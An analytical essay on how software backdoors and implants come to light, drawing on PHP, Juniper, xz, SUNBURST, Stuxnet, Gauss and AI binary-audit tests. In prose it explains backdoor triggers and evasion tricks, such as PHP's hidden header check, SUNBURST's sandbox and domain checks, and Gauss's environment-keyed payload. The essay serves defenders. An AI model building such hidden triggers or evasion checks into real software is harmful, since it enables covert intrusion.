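PHP is a programming language that runs on the servers of many websites. On 28 March 2021, somebody added eleven lines to its source code under the name of PHP's creator, Rasmus Lerdorf, and described the change as fixing a typo. PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021) reproduces the added code, which checked web requests for a header called "User-Agentt", the standard "User-Agent" with an extra t. If this header contained the word "zerodium", the server skipped the header's first eight characters and ran the rest as PHP code. An attacker could therefore have run any commands on a website that used this version.

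Nikita Popov, one of PHP's main maintainers, removed the lines after he and his colleagues noticed them during a routine review of recent changes, according to WeLiveSecurity (2021). Seven hours later somebody put the same code back, this time under Popov's name, and another maintainer, Levi Morrison, removed it again. The backdoor was gone within 12 hours and never appeared in a release.

This was a success for source review, because the maintainers had no symptom or failed comparison to guide them. It was also an easy test. The backdoor contained the text "REMOVETHIS: sold to zerodium, mid 2017", which refers to a company that buys exploits, and PHP.Watch remarks that the backdoor was barely disguised. Craig Young of the security company Tripwire told SC Magazine that the description had exposed the attacker, since a typo fix should not introduce new code. A reviewer could notice that mismatch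 before working out what the code did.

The maintainers found it harder to learn how the attacker had got in. Git, the system that stores PHP's source code, accepts any name as the author of a change, so the names on the changes did not help. Popov at first blamed a break-in at the project's own server, but *PHP's Git Server Compromised* (2021) quotes his 7 April update saying the maintainers no longer believed this.

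Reviewers took far longer to find two backdoors in Juniper Networks firewalls. On 17 December 2015 Juniper announced that an internal code review had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen firewalls. One backdoor let an intruder log in remotely with a secret password, and the other let an eavesdropper decrypt the private connections (VPNs) that customers ran through the firewall. *Much ado about Juniper* (Caudill, 2015) dates the first release with unauthorised code to September 2012, more than three years before the announcement.

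Juniper called the review "recent" and "internal" in its announcement, but did not say what prompted it. It may have been a customer's complaint or a strange log entry. The case is therefore weaker evidence than the PHP one that routine code reading finds implants, although people often cite it as a success of code review.

Outsiders needed little time once they knew there was something to find. Rapid7's *CVE-2015-7755* (2015) reports that an employee of the security company Fox-IT said his firm had identified the secret password in six hours. By then a quick search had found about 26,000 NetScreen devices that accepted SSH connections from the internet.

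The VPN backdoor would have been particularly hard to recognise by reading the code. The firewalls generated random numbers for encryption with a method called Dual EC, which relies on a fixed constant. Somebody who chooses this constant in a certain way can predict all later output from a few bytes of it. The attacker only had to replace Juniper's constant with another. Both are long numbers with no visible meaning, so a reader who saw only the new version would have had no reason to suspect it. Comparing it with an older version would have revealed the change immediately, though not its purpose.

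### What Linux's reviewers let through

Wu and Lu, two researchers at the University of Minnesota, tested whether Linux's reviewers would catch flaws added on purpose. *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, their paper on the test, uses the term "hypocrite commits" for apparently useful fixes that also introduce a vulnerability. Between 4 and 21 August 2020, they sent the kernel developers five patches under two invented identities. In April 2021, after the kernel developers protested, Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew the paper because they had experimented on the developers without their consent.

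TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches* reports that the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board found that none of the experiment's buggy code reached the main version of the kernel. Slashdot's *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith* quotes an account that three of the patches contained real bugs and that the developers accepted none of them, though not always because of the bug. The experiment therefore doesn't prove that the reviewers missed the planted flaws, or show that they recognised every one.

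Three patches are also too few to measure how good the reviewers were. If they normally accepted half of all such patches, they would still reject all three one time in eight.

The aftermath provided better evidence. The kernel developers went back over 435 changes from the university, most of which they had accepted in earlier years. Neowin's *Here is Linux Advisory Board's ruling on University of Minnesota's "hypocrite commits"* (2021) gives the results:

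| Result of the second review | Changes |
|---|---|
| Correct | 349 |
| Incorrect and still in need of repair | 39 |
| Already fixed by a later change | 25 |
| No longer relevant | 12 |
| Made before the research group existed | 9 |
| Withdrawn at the author's request | 1 |

The incorrect changes and those that somebody had already fixed total 64 of the 435, or about 15%. The kernel developer Cook (2021) stressed that these flaws were unintentional, unlike those in the hypocrite commits. The first reviewers had missed them. Finding the 39 that nobody had yet fixed took a special effort by many people. A reader commenting on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) counted 85 developers whom the report thanked for this work.

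A deniable backdoor looks like an honest mistake, so it would be about as likely to get past reviewers. But the 15% figure doesn't estimate that likelihood, because an incorrect change need not create a security hole and the university's patches may have been worse than average. The second reviewers also knew which changes to distrust, a warning that reviewers don't have when a well-behaved stranger like Jia Tan sends in a first patch.

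### Narrowing down what to read

Comparing two files is simplest when they should be identical. A new release is supposed to differ from the last one, so somebody has to read a long list of changes. *Not In My Git Yard*, a paper from July 2026, gives the example of vsFTPd, a file-transfer server. An attacker had added a backdoor triggered by any user name containing ":)" to one of its releases. The difference between that release and the previous one spans five files and 1,407 lines.

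The paper presents a tool called Lily that picks out the suspicious part. It relies on a fuzzer, a program that feeds another program large numbers of varied inputs. For vsFTPd, it worked as follows:

1. The fuzzer tried different inputs on the new release until a user name with ":)" in it made the server run code that no earlier input had reached.
2. Lily detected that the server was behaving in a way that the inputs saved from the previous release had not produced.
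3. It looked for code that was both new in this release and active during the strange behaviour.
4. Within that code, it highlighted the places that made the unusual requests to the operating system.

Lily has to run the program, so it combines comparison with a search for runtime anomalies, and it leaves a person with far less to read. But the fuzzer must first find the trigger. It can find a two-character trigger by trial and error, but it could never have guessed a command signed with the xz attacker's private key.

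### AI models as readers of machine code

Lily's comparison requires an earlier version and the source code, but owners of routers and other devices often have only the compiled program. For a long time, automated tools were little help with compiled programs. *ROSA* (2025), which presents another fuzzing-based detector, says the field had made no significant advance in more than seven years.

AI models can now do some of this work. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) introduced a test called BinaryAudit. They added backdoors to open-source network programs, such as the web server lighttpd, and gave the models the compiled programs without the source code. The models could use standard reverse engineering tools, and in most tasks had to name the exact address of the function that contained the backdoor. A skilled person could find this kind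 of backdoor fairly easily.

The best model in that first round, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of these tasks. Across all the models, 28% of answers on clean programs reported a backdoor or another problem that did not exist. This rate varied greatly between models. In the ranking on Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, Gemini 3.1 Pro also found 49% of the backdoors and wrongly flagged 17% of the clean programs, while a version of GPT-5.2 Codex found 46% and flagged no clean programs. The benchmark has only 33 tasks in total, so the zero rate was measured on a small number of clean programs.

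These figures are probably too low for the best models of late 2026, which the ranking does not include. The top score rose from 21% for a model released in March 2025 to 49% for one released in February 2026.

In one successful case, Claude Opus 4.5 took five minutes to find a backdoor in the web server lighttpd that ran any command it received in a certain HTTP header. The model first searched the program for suspicious text and found nothing. It then listed the outside functions each library used and saw that one library called popen, which runs commands. Popen has legitimate uses, so the model traced the call back to a function named li_check_debug_header, decompiled it and confirmed that the server used it. The method was sound, but the function's name had survived compilation and was a strong hint.

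Claude Opus 4.6 did worse on dnsmasq, a program that assigns network addresses to computers. Grabowski and colleagues had added seven lines that ran any command arriving in a certain kind of network message. The model found the right function and saw that it ran a command, but assumed this was dnsmasq's normal way of running scripts and moved on without checking where the command came from. Fedora's testers had made much the same mistake with xz.

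Models also reported vulnerabilities that did not exist. Gemini 3 Pro reported that an attacker could run commands through one of a server's settings, but the source code showed that the program accepted only a number there and never executed it. Quarkslab, a security company, saw similar errors in 2026 when it tested models up to Claude Opus 5 on programs with deliberately obscured code. Some reports described harmless protective code as a backdoor, and the wrong reports were worded as confidently as the right ones. Somebody therefore still has to check the code that a model points to, which is much quicker than searching the whole program.

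### Screening thousands of files a day

A model's great advantage over a human analyst is that it can read far more files. VirusTotal, a service that checks files people upload, receives more than two million a day. Quintero, Bennett and Tarter (2025) estimate in *Reversing at Scale* that even in large operations, analysts closely read fewer than 1% of new files. This helps explain how a Stuxnet sample could go unrecognised for years after somebody submitted it to such a service.

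On 18 October 2025 VirusTotal ran an AI system on all 9,981 programs for Apple devices that it first received that day. Many compiled programs are too long for a model to read whole, so other software first extracted the most informative parts, such as readable text, the outside functions each program used and summaries of selected functions. The model judged each program from this extract, without seeing antivirus results. It flagged 164 programs as malicious, while more than 70 antivirus engines together flagged 67.

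Quintero and colleagues then examined the disagreements. Thirty of the antivirus detections were mistakes by Microsoft's engine, which Microsoft confirmed and corrected, and three more were cracked programs that did nothing malicious in themselves. In the other direction, the model had flagged nearly 100 programs that no antivirus engine had. Several of these were clearly malware, including these two:

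- One Mac program downloaded and ran a further script, then sent data from the computer to the attacker. No antivirus engine flagged it on the first day, but eleven did by 28 October.
- A piece of iPhone software promised free access to paid features in Adobe Lightroom, and also showed users a fake login window to steal their passwords. No antivirus engine had flagged it by 3 November.

Many of the other programs were merely dubious, such as adware and game cheats. At least one, a component of a programmer's tool, was harmless. The model correctly described how it communicated but mistook this for an attacker's control channel. Quintero and colleagues do not say how many false alarms there were in total. Checking only the cases where the model and the antivirus engines disagreed also cannot reveal malware that both missed.

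The test was easier in one respect than finding an implant like SUNBURST, because the Mac and iPhone examples were standalone malicious programs, whereas SUNBURST was a small addition to a large and useful product. An extract that leaves out most of a program's functions may leave out the few that contain the implant.

Researchers also look for malicious releases in public package libraries. Datadog Security Labs, for example, found disguised code in four AsyncAPI packages on npm, the main library of JavaScript packages, and traced it to a single change in one of the project's GitHub repositories. Such reports cover only the malicious releases that somebody caught, so they cannot show what share goes undetected. To measure that share, researchers would have to test scanners on packages whose contents they already knew, as BinaryAudit does for models that read compiled programs.

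## What does a dormant or narrowly targeted implant leave to notice?

Many implants do nothing harmful until a particular date, machine or message triggers them. Some are impossible to notice while they run dormant, but several famous ones could be noticed in that state. Freund, for instance, noticed the xz backdoor without anybody having triggered it.

Suppose somebody hides code in a hotel's door-lock program that opens every room at midnight on New Year's Eve. People could detect it at three different moments:

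- **Being present.** All year, the extra code is in the program's file, where a reader or a comparison could find it.
- **Checking the trigger.** The code has to look at the clock again and again. Other implants also have to load themselves, hide or spread before they can check anything.
- **Acting.** On the night itself, the doors open.

Only the last of these requires the trigger. How much can be noticed before the trigger occurs depends largely on what the trigger is and how the implant checks for it.

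### Waiting and looking around

SUNBURST, the implant in SolarWinds' Orion program, waited almost two weeks before it contacted its makers. Eckels, Smith and Ballenthin (2020), in *SUNBURST Additional Technical Details*, list what it checked first:

- It had to be running inside the right part of Orion.
- The infected file had to be at least 12 to 14 days old. SUNBURST picked the exact threshold at random.
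- The computer had to belong to a Windows domain, a centrally managed network of the kind most large organisations have. The domain's name could not contain "test", "solarwinds" or any of several other terms that probably referred to SolarWinds' own internal networks.
- The computer had to be able to look up one of SolarWinds' internet addresses.
- No program or driver from a long list of security and analysis tools could be running.

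Analysts often run a suspicious file in a sandbox, an isolated computer where it can do no damage, and watch what it does. Kaspersky's researchers thought the long wait was why SUNBURST was so hard to spot this way, according to Global Security Mag's *Kaspersky shares initial analysis into the Sunburst malware*. The wait would also have outlasted the three-day cooldown that PyPI gives as an example. A tester could have set the clock forward, but SUNBURST would still have stopped in a typical sandbox, which has analysis tools running and doesn't belong to a company's domain.

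Hacioglu (2026), in *When Malware Does Math*, points out that inactivity can be a sign that malware has detected a sandbox. This is useful when the suspicious file has no other function. It would not have helped with SUNBURST, because the rest of Orion kept working normally.

Even on a computer that passed every check, SUNBURST waited for instructions from the attackers before activating its payload. It received them through DNS, the system computers use to look up the address of a named server. SUNBURST looked up a name under avsvmcloud.com that contained the victim's domain name in coded form, and the address that came back was the instruction. Depending on the address, SUNBURST kept waiting, started taking detailed commands, or shut down for good. Because the attackers chose their victims on their own server, nobody could have learned from the code which of the nearly 18,000 customers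 they wanted.

The attackers behind Operation Triangulation also made the final choice of targets on their own server, which sent the TriangleDB implant to an iPhone only after receiving the results of two programs that checked the phone. Kaspersky found that the first did odd calculations, such as the logarithm of −1, and drew the yellow triangle that gave the campaign its name. The triangle's exact pixels helped to identify the device. The second program listed the phone's apps and running processes and searched for signs of a jailbreak, the removal of Apple's restrictions. Researchers often need to jailbreak a phone to examine it.

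### One plant, one calculation

Stuxnet spread widely but acted on very few machines. Symantec's *Stuxnet Dossier* estimates that it had infected about 100,000 computers by 29 September 2010, about 60% of them in Iran. Its payload needed a computer with Siemens' Step 7 software, connected to one particular model of industrial controller. That controller had to be set up to communicate with at least 33 frequency converters (devices that control the speed of motors) from either of two makers, one in Finland and one in Tehran.

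When Stuxnet found such a controller, it changed the controller's code and then watched the motors:

1. It counted reports from the converters that showed them running between 807 and 1,210 Hz. It needed about 13 days of these.
2. It waited another two hours.
3. It raised the frequency to 1,410 Hz for about 15 minutes, then let normal operation resume.
4. After about 27 more days of normal readings, it lowered the frequency to 2 Hz and then set it to 1,064 Hz. This stage took about 50 minutes.
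5. It went on alternating between the two attacks, about 27 days apart.

Few machines run at such speeds. Symantec's *Stuxnet breakthrough* notes that the United States restricts exports of efficient frequency converters with outputs above 600 Hz, because they can be used to enrich uranium. Engineers at a factory with an infected computer and an ordinary conveyor belt would never have seen the payload act.

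The 2005 sabotage program fast16, which researchers identified two decades later, had an even narrower trigger. It waited for a physics simulation to reach a certain stage. Reversemode's *Inside Fast16's Physics Sabotage Engine* (2026) describes how it followed the simulation's progress and recorded the highest value reached so far. Once the simulation had gone far enough, fast16 left low values alone, changed middle ones linearly and replaced high ones with a fixed figure. Engineers would have seen a wrong but perhaps plausible answer rather than a crash. Reversemode could not identify the physical process being simulated. CNews' *Один из самых старых вредоносов АНБ США искажал результаты ядерных симуляций* (2026), a Russian news report from two months later, says the aim was to slow a nuclear programme.

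According to SecurityWeek, researchers at the security company SentinelOne found fast16 while searching for the earliest Windows malware that used the programming language Lua, not while investigating a strange result.

### A payload nobody could read

Analysts could read the code of Stuxnet and fast16, including the conditions the programs checked. Gauss, a spying program that Kaspersky made public in August 2012, had an encrypted payload that they could not read. The payload was in a part of Gauss that travelled on USB sticks, and its key depended on the names of folders on the target's computer. Kaspersky (2012) had recorded more than 2,500 Gauss infections since late May of that year.

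Securelist's *The Mystery of the Encrypted Gauss Payload*, from Kaspersky's research site, explains the procedure:

1. Gauss lists the folders in which Windows looks for programs. It adds any folder in Program Files whose name starts with a character that comes after "z" in the computer's character table, such as "~" or an Arabic or Hebrew letter.
2. It joins these names in every possible pair and adds some fixed bytes to each pair.
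3. It computes a hash, or fingerprint, of each pair and then hashes the result another 10,000 times.
4. It compares the final fingerprint with one stored in its code. If no pair matches, it stops.
5. If a pair matches, Gauss hashes the same names again with different fixed bytes. The result gives it the key to decrypt and run the payload.

The stored fingerprint lets Gauss recognise the right names without containing them. An analyst can only guess names and test them, and the repeated hashing slows every guess. Kaspersky's staff tried millions of combinations without success, then asked the public for help, but no one seems to have found the answer. The staff noted that the payload was big enough to contain code for attacking industrial equipment, as Stuxnet's did, but this was speculation.

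Hashed secrets in other implants have been easier to recover. SUNBURST stored its list of security tools as hashes, and volunteers recovered the names. Triangulation's second checking program held hashes of 40 Apple accounts that the attackers used, and Kaspersky recovered most of them. People could guess these because the names of security products are public and email addresses follow familiar patterns. Gauss was harder because it needed an exact pair of folder names, one of them probably belonging to a rare program.

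Thomas and Francillon call detection complete only when the analyst has mapped every part of the trigger and the payload. By that standard, Kaspersky found Gauss but did not fully detect its hidden payload. Kaspersky's staff knew how the trigger worked, but not what would satisfy it or what the payload would do.

### A key only the attacker holds

The trigger for the xz backdoor was a message that only the attacker could write. Securelist's *XZ backdoor* traces what happened when somebody connected to an infected server using an SSH certificate, a kind of digital identity card that contains a cryptographic key:

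1. The backdoor read the large number at the heart of that key. An attacker could pack a command into this number.
2. It did a small calculation on the first few fields. The answer had to be between 0 and 3, which was also the type of command.
3. It decrypted the rest.
4. It checked the command's digital signature. Anyone with the backdoor's file could extract the public key for checking signatures, but making one required a private key, which the attacker kept.
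5. It checked that the signed data included a fingerprint of this particular server, so that nobody could record a command sent to one server and use it on another.

If a check failed, the server handled the login as usual. Filippo Valsorda, who relayed the first analysts' findings the day after Freund's announcement, concluded that nobody could write a reliable network scanner for infected servers. Without the private key, a scanner would get the same response from an infected server as from a clean one.

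The secret password in Juniper's firewalls gave much less protection, because anyone who found it in the code could use it to log in or to test whether a firewall had the backdoor. Reading the xz code revealed what the attacker could do without letting anyone else do it.

Attackers can also leave the payload out of the implant until they need it. TechRadar's *New Windows malware lays dormant until a custom command activates it* describes SLEEPWALKER, which the researcher Dominik Reichel found in 2026. It is disguised as a component of ESET's security software and can stay idle for weeks until it receives special network signals. TechRadar reports that the implant itself contains no malicious code. Reading such a program could show that it is built to receive commands, but presumably not what those commands would be.

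### What a million clean tests show

If a fraction p of all inputs to a program contain an implant's trigger, a test on one randomly chosen input has a 1 − p chance of missing it, and the chance that n independent tests all miss it is (1 − p)ⁿ.

Setting this chance to 5% and solving for p gives about 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. If the trigger were more common than that, the tester would have had at least a 95% chance of meeting it. A thousand clean tests therefore give an upper bound on the trigger's frequency of about three inputs in a thousand, and a million clean tests give about three in a million.

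Random tests that find nothing are good evidence against a common trigger but almost none against a rare one. If one input in a trillion contains the trigger, a million random tests have about a one-in-a-million chance of including it. A 95% chance would require about three trillion tests, which would take 95 years at a thousand tests a second. The same arithmetic applies to random tests of a neural network.

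The calculation also treats the tests as independent, an assumption that real implants violate. A million tests of Orion on the day of installation would all have fallen within the same 12-day wait. For SUNBURST or Stuxnet, the relevant sample size is the number of different computers or plants tested, not the number of inputs tried on each. Even if Stuxnet's payload had acted on none of a thousand randomly chosen infected computers, about 300 of the 100,000 could still have been targets.

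The bound also describes only how often the trigger turns up by chance. The right signed message would practically never reach an xz server by accident, but the attacker could send one at any time, so a very low frequency in testing is weak evidence of safety.

Testers can do much better when they have some idea of the trigger. They can change the date, imitate a company network or use a fuzzer that keeps inputs that reach new code. Lily found the ":)" in vsFTPd with that kind of fuzzer. But Kaspersky's staff knew exactly how Gauss checked its trigger, and their millions of guesses still failed.

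### Was the implant silent until it acted?

Testing often cannot set off the payload, but all five of these implants did something observable beforehand:

| Implant | What it did before the payload acted | Did this lead to the discovery? |
|---|---|---|
| xz | Delayed each start of the login server by about half a second | Yes |
| Stuxnet | Crashed Windows computers, probably through its supporting code, and contacted its makers' servers | Yes, through the crashes |
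| Triangulation | Sent details of the phone to a checking server | Partly, as one step in the traffic pattern |
| SUNBURST | Looked up coded names and disabled security services | No, FireEye began with an unfamiliar phone |
| Gauss | Wrote details of the computer to a hidden-looking file on the USB stick | No, Kaspersky noticed its resemblance to Flame, another spying program |

The delay that Freund traced in xz came from the backdoor's search of the symbol tables, not from checking the attacker's signature. This search ran every time sshd started, whether or not the attacker ever connected.

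In Triangulation, the attackers' precautions created evidence. They added the first checking program to keep their implant away from researchers, but its short exchange with backuprabbit.com appeared in Kaspersky's Wi-Fi records and became part of the pattern by which researchers discovered the attack.

SUNBURST left visible traces that people did not recognise. When it found certain security services on a computer, it changed a Windows setting so they would not start after the next reboot. It also kept making DNS lookups, at random intervals of up to nine hours. Unit 42 later searched its company's DNS records and found such lookups from April to November 2020. They had gone unrecognised because computers look up names constantly, and nobody yet knew that the domain being looked up mattered.

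Unit 42's company, Palo Alto Networks, saw both stages on its own Orion server. The server looked up one of the coded names on 29 September 2020, and nothing harmful followed. The company isolated the server and investigated only after the blocked payload of 5 October. The earlier lookup was a runtime trace, but it was useful as a warning only in hindsight.

A dormant implant can have no noticeable effect if its check takes almost no computation, uses only information the program already has, and needs no extra code to load or hide it. The cash machine's test for 9999, PHP's test for an extra header and the two lines in Linux were all checks of this kind. Until somebody triggered them, no user could have noticed them, and they could be found only by reading or comparing the code.

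Attackers who want a check this hard to notice can write it into the program's source code, but a reviewer may then read it. The xz attacker avoided this by hiding compiled code in test files, but that code had to do complicated work every time sshd started. SolarWinds' attackers avoided both problems with SUNSPOT, which made SUNBURST a normal part of Orion without leaving it in the stored source. After that, most of the signs of SUNBURST came from its lookups and its interference with security tools, rather than from loading itself.

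Some implants are hard to notice even after they start acting. Triangulation's microphone module could stop recording when the phone's screen came on, and it recorded only if the battery was more than 10% charged. Juniper's VPN backdoor let an eavesdropper decrypt recorded traffic on another computer, so the firewall would have behaved the same way whether or not anyone was using the backdoor.

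## Does the list of discovered implants mislead?

A list of known implants contains only those that somebody found, so whatever makes an implant easy to find will be more common on the list than among implants in general. Judging all implants by those on the list is survivorship bias, the error of judging a whole group by the members that got through some filter. Slow logins, crashes and strange connections led to many of the best-known discoveries, but even if every account of a discovery is accurate, this doesn't show that watching software run is the best way to find implants.

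A list of known implants can miss one that has been in use for years. Even a careful list compiled in 2022 would have left out Operation Triangulation, whose attackers had been infecting iPhones since at least 2019.

### A hundred imaginary implants

Suppose attackers have planted 100 implants. Forty are noisy, meaning they cause a symptom that a monitor could catch, and 60 are quiet. Monitoring finds half of the noisy implants and none of the quiet ones. Reviewers, working independently, find a tenth of each kind.

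| | Noisy | Quiet | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| All implants | 40 | 60 | 100 |
| Monitoring finds | 20 | 0 | 20 |
| Review finds | 4 | 6 | 10 |
| Both find | 2 | 0 | 2 |
| At least one finds | 22 | 6 | 28 |
| Neither finds | 18 | 54 | 72 |

Monitoring for anomalies found 20 of the 28 known implants, or 71%. That doesn't mean it finds most implants, because it found only those 20 of the 100 that existed. The list also overrepresents noisy implants, which make up 79% of the known implants but only 40% of all 100.

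If nobody had reviewed any code, the list would have contained 20 implants, all noisy and all found by monitoring. It would have been the same if there had been 6,000 quiet implants instead of 60.

These numbers are invented, so they aren't evidence that most real implants are quiet. In the example, monitoring finds twice as many implants as review does. But even perfect monitoring would add only the 18 remaining noisy implants, while better review could find any of the 72.

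### Why do known malicious packages act at once?

Real collections of malicious software have the same problem. *An Empirical Study of Observability Limits in Advanced Software Supply Chain Attacks* (Tan, Brierley and colleagues, 2026) examined 16,272 malicious packages collected by the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group. Of the 16,223 with a recorded trigger, 15,583 act when somebody installs them and 594 when somebody downloads them. Only 46, or 0.3%, have any other trigger.

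The figure of 99.7% has two possible explanations. Attackers may rarely wait, because a thief wants passwords quickly and installation may be the only time the package's code is sure to run. Or the collection may miss packages that do wait, because it records what packages did in isolated sandboxes. A package that stayed inactive for two weeks, as SUNBURST did, might look harmless there and never enter the collection.

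In *Batten Down Your Packages*, written for Google, Vanderlee and Carrera (2026) similarly describe attacks on open-source packages as "noisy once enabled" and say that people usually discover them much sooner than attacks on a company's own code or update system. In March 2026, malicious versions of the axios package, which has over 100 million downloads a week, were removed within three hours. In contrast, attackers controlled the update servers for the text editor Notepad++ from June to December 2025.

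Vanderlee and Carrera count only a "handful of identified cases" of the second kind of attack in 2025 and early 2026, and are highly confident that such attacks remain rare. They may be right, since these attacks take more planning and money. But their count is a minimum, because most of the cases they identified were espionage aimed at a few chosen victims, and attacks like that are the most likely to go unnoticed.

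Trends are also hard to interpret. Vanderlee and Carrera cite OpenSSF figures showing that the number of malicious packages identified rose by 1,444% from 2024 to 2025. Some of the increase must be real, because Google also saw larger attack campaigns, but better scanning would raise the count even if attackers had done nothing new.

### Good stories and unequal effort

Lists of famous implants are also biased because people choose cases that make good stories. A customer discovered the attack on Codecov by comparing two checksums, which is less memorable than an engineer noticing half a second of delay.

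Far more hours also go into running software than into reviewing it. A library installed on 10,000 servers runs for 7.2 million hours in a 30-day month, while two reviewers who each spend a working day on its latest release put in about 16 hours. If somebody finds an implant because a server behaves oddly, this does not show that monitoring finds more implants than review does for the same effort.

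An hour of a server running is not equivalent to an hour of someone reading code, because nobody is watching the server most of the time. A fair comparison would count the time people spend looking at alerts and investigating them, including when they find nothing. Stories of successful discoveries leave out most of that time, so an organisation can't use them to decide whether to spend its next hundred hours on monitoring or on reading code.

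The list also understates how much review catches. When a reviewer rejects a malicious change, it never enters the program, and often nobody learns that it was malicious. If a real attacker had sent Linux's developers the University of Minnesota's faulty patches, the rejections would probably have looked routine, and no list of implants would include the patches.

Monitoring has also had successes that the list leaves out. For example, Fedora's Richard Jones blocked the xz backdoor while working around what seemed to be an ordinary fault. It is therefore unclear which discovery method the list over-represents overall, although it almost certainly contains too few quiet implants.

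### What leaked documents add

A list of implants that does not depend on detection would be a better check. The people who make implants have such lists, and some of their documents have leaked.

In 2017 WikiLeaks published Vault 7, a collection of documents about the CIA's hacking tools. It included a dated changelog for a program called Fluxwire. Symantec's *Longhorn* compares the changelog with samples of a spying program that the company had been tracking as Corentry. New features appeared in the samples on the dates in the changelog or a few days later, so Symantec concluded that Fluxwire and Corentry were the same program.

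| Period in the changelog | Versions | Samples in Symantec's comparison |
|---|---|---|
| January 2011 to February 2013 | 2.1.0 to 2.4.1 | None |
| August 2013 to February 2015 | Six, from 3.0.0 to 3.3.0 | Five of the six |
| May to November 2015 | 3.3.1 to 3.5.0 | None |

The group that used the program had been active since at least 2011, but Symantec first noticed it in 2014, when the group carried out an attack using a Word document that exploited a previously unknown flaw. The samples therefore cover the period around the discovery well but don't cover the earlier years at all. Some of the missing versions may never have been used against anyone, so a gap doesn't necessarily mean that Symantec missed an implant. The comparison also measures only how well Symantec followed a group it knew about, not how many other groups it had never noticed.

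Another leak in 2017 provides some evidence on that question. An unidentified group called the Shadow Brokers published tools stolen from the National Security Agency (NSA), which spies on foreign communications for the United States. The tools included scripts that NSA operators ran on computers they had broken into, to check whether other governments' hackers were already there. The Intercept's *Leaked Files Show How the NSA Tracks Other Countries’ Hackers* (2018) reports that in 2013 these scripts looked for signs of at least 45 state operations, some of which may still have been unknown to outside researchers. The NSA also seems to have been tracking tools of a group called Dark Hotel in 2011, about three years before the wider security community discovered them.

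This list still depends on detection, but the NSA could look from inside machines that no security company had access to. It also had other sources of information. One of the 45 entries appears to be for Stuxnet, which the NSA or its allies had reportedly built. According to a former official, the NSA team added it in 2010, after Stuxnet began spreading out of control.

The same leak contained a list of driver names, with advice to NSA operators on what to do if they came across each one. For fast16, the 2005 sabotage program, the advice was "Nothing to see here – carry on". According to SentinelLABS's *fast16* (2026), the research team searched old malware collections and connected the program to the leaked name through a file that contained a path naming fast16.

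By then the name had been public for nine years and the program had been on VirusTotal for nearly a decade, yet only one antivirus engine there classified it as malicious, with limited confidence. At least one sophisticated implant therefore escaped public notice for about two decades, although people had the file and a clue to its importance.

fast16's design also made it less likely to be noticed. Before spreading to a computer, it normally looked for signs of 18 security products and stopped if it found any. SUNBURST had a similar check. If implants avoid well-protected computers, security companies' customers will report fewer implants than they would if infections were random.

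### Quiet implants with noisy relatives

A quiet implant can still get onto the list if it resembles a noisy one. Analysts recognised the 2007 version of Stuxnet, which was already in a malware collection, only after the crashes of 2010 had led them to a later version they could compare it with. Kaspersky found Gauss because it resembled Flame, and researchers found the reviewdog compromise only after the one at tj-actions.

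Implants can also be discovered because of the machine they are on. The Intercept describes a computer at a research institute in the Middle East on which Kaspersky found tools from six groups in 2014. Once investigators have a reason to examine a machine thoroughly, they may find implants that would never have attracted attention by themselves. NSA operators knew this, and might withdraw from a machine if they found reckless hackers there who could expose them too.

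These discoveries depend less on how noisy each implant was, so they are useful evidence about the quiet ones. But we can't tell from them how many quiet implants have no known relatives and no noisy neighbours. Even for Stuxnet, McDonald and colleagues wrote in 2013 that more versions were known to exist but that nobody had recovered them.

### How long do intruders go unnoticed?

Figures on dwell time seem to offer a more systematic answer. The best-known figures, from Google's Mandiant, cover all kinds of break-ins, many of which involve stolen passwords rather than an implant in the victim's software. The *M-Trends 2026 Report* (2026) gives a median dwell time of 14 days for the attacks Mandiant investigated in 2025, up from 11 days the year before. The median for espionage was 122 days. Intrusions with BRICKSTORM, a backdoor that attackers install on network equipment that cannot run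 ordinary security software, lasted an average of 393 days.

These figures include only intrusions that somebody discovered. Suppose intruders break into ten companies on the same day. Four companies notice after 5 days, two after 400 days, and four never do. The median dwell time of the six discovered intrusions is 5 days, but the median for all ten is 400 days.

Recent attacks are especially likely to look short-lived. An implant inserted in December 2025 and discovered by December 2026 lasted at most a year. Recent implants that will stay hidden for five years are not in the figures yet.

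Some recorded dwell times may also be too low. Kutscher (2026) warns in *M-Trends 2026* that many organisations keep logs for only 90 days, so investigators cannot see how an intrusion of nearly 400 days began. If the earliest surviving trace is three months old, the intruder may have arrived much earlier.

A longer median can even be a good sign. Kutscher thinks the rise from 11 to 14 days probably reflects attackers' growing skill at evading defences. Mandiant attributes it largely to long-running intrusions by spies and by North Koreans hired as remote IT workers. But if defenders had become better at uncovering old intrusions, adding those to the figures would also have raised the median.

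Mandiant also records who first noticed each intrusion:

| Who alerted the victim, 2025 | All investigations | Ransomware |
|---|---|---|
| Its own staff or systems | 52% | 41% |
| An outside organisation | 34% | 15% |
| The attacker | 14% | 44% |

The ransomware column is unusually informative because attackers who want a ransom have to tell the victim about the attack. The figures therefore include many intrusions that nobody else noticed, which account for 44% of the cases. Spies don't announce themselves, so if victims of espionage overlook intruders as often as victims of ransomware do, many espionage intrusions will be missing from the figures.

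Mandiant's summary groups intrusions by who noticed them, but not by how. A victim's own staff could have discovered an intrusion by following up a strange connection, comparing files or reading code.

### Which datasets record how an attack came to light?

No public dataset of supply-chain attacks appears to record systematically how people discovered each one. The Atlantic Council, an American think tank, maintains one of the main collections. *Software supply chain security* (Loomis, Scott and colleagues, 2023) reports that it had grown to 250 entries by 2023, made up of 168 attacks and 82 disclosed vulnerabilities. The Atlantic Council's *Breaking Trust Database Codebook* (2020) defines fields for the affected code, how the attackers changed and distributed it, who they were and what damage they could do, but none for how the attack was discovered.

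The collection isn't reliable for calculating dwell times either. If nobody knows when an attack began, the Atlantic Council enters the date of discovery instead, which would make the dwell time appear to be zero.

Other collections have different aims. IQT Labs' *software-supply-chain-compromises* (2020), now archived, gathers publicly reported attacks and sorts them by report date because that is the only sortable field filled in for every entry. *SoK* (2024), a review of supply-chain defences, uses this collection because it records the point where attackers got in. *A Retrospective Survey of 2024/2025 Open Source Supply Chain Compromises* also classifies cases by how the attacker first gained access, and its author complains that people usually write much more about what attackers did afterwards.

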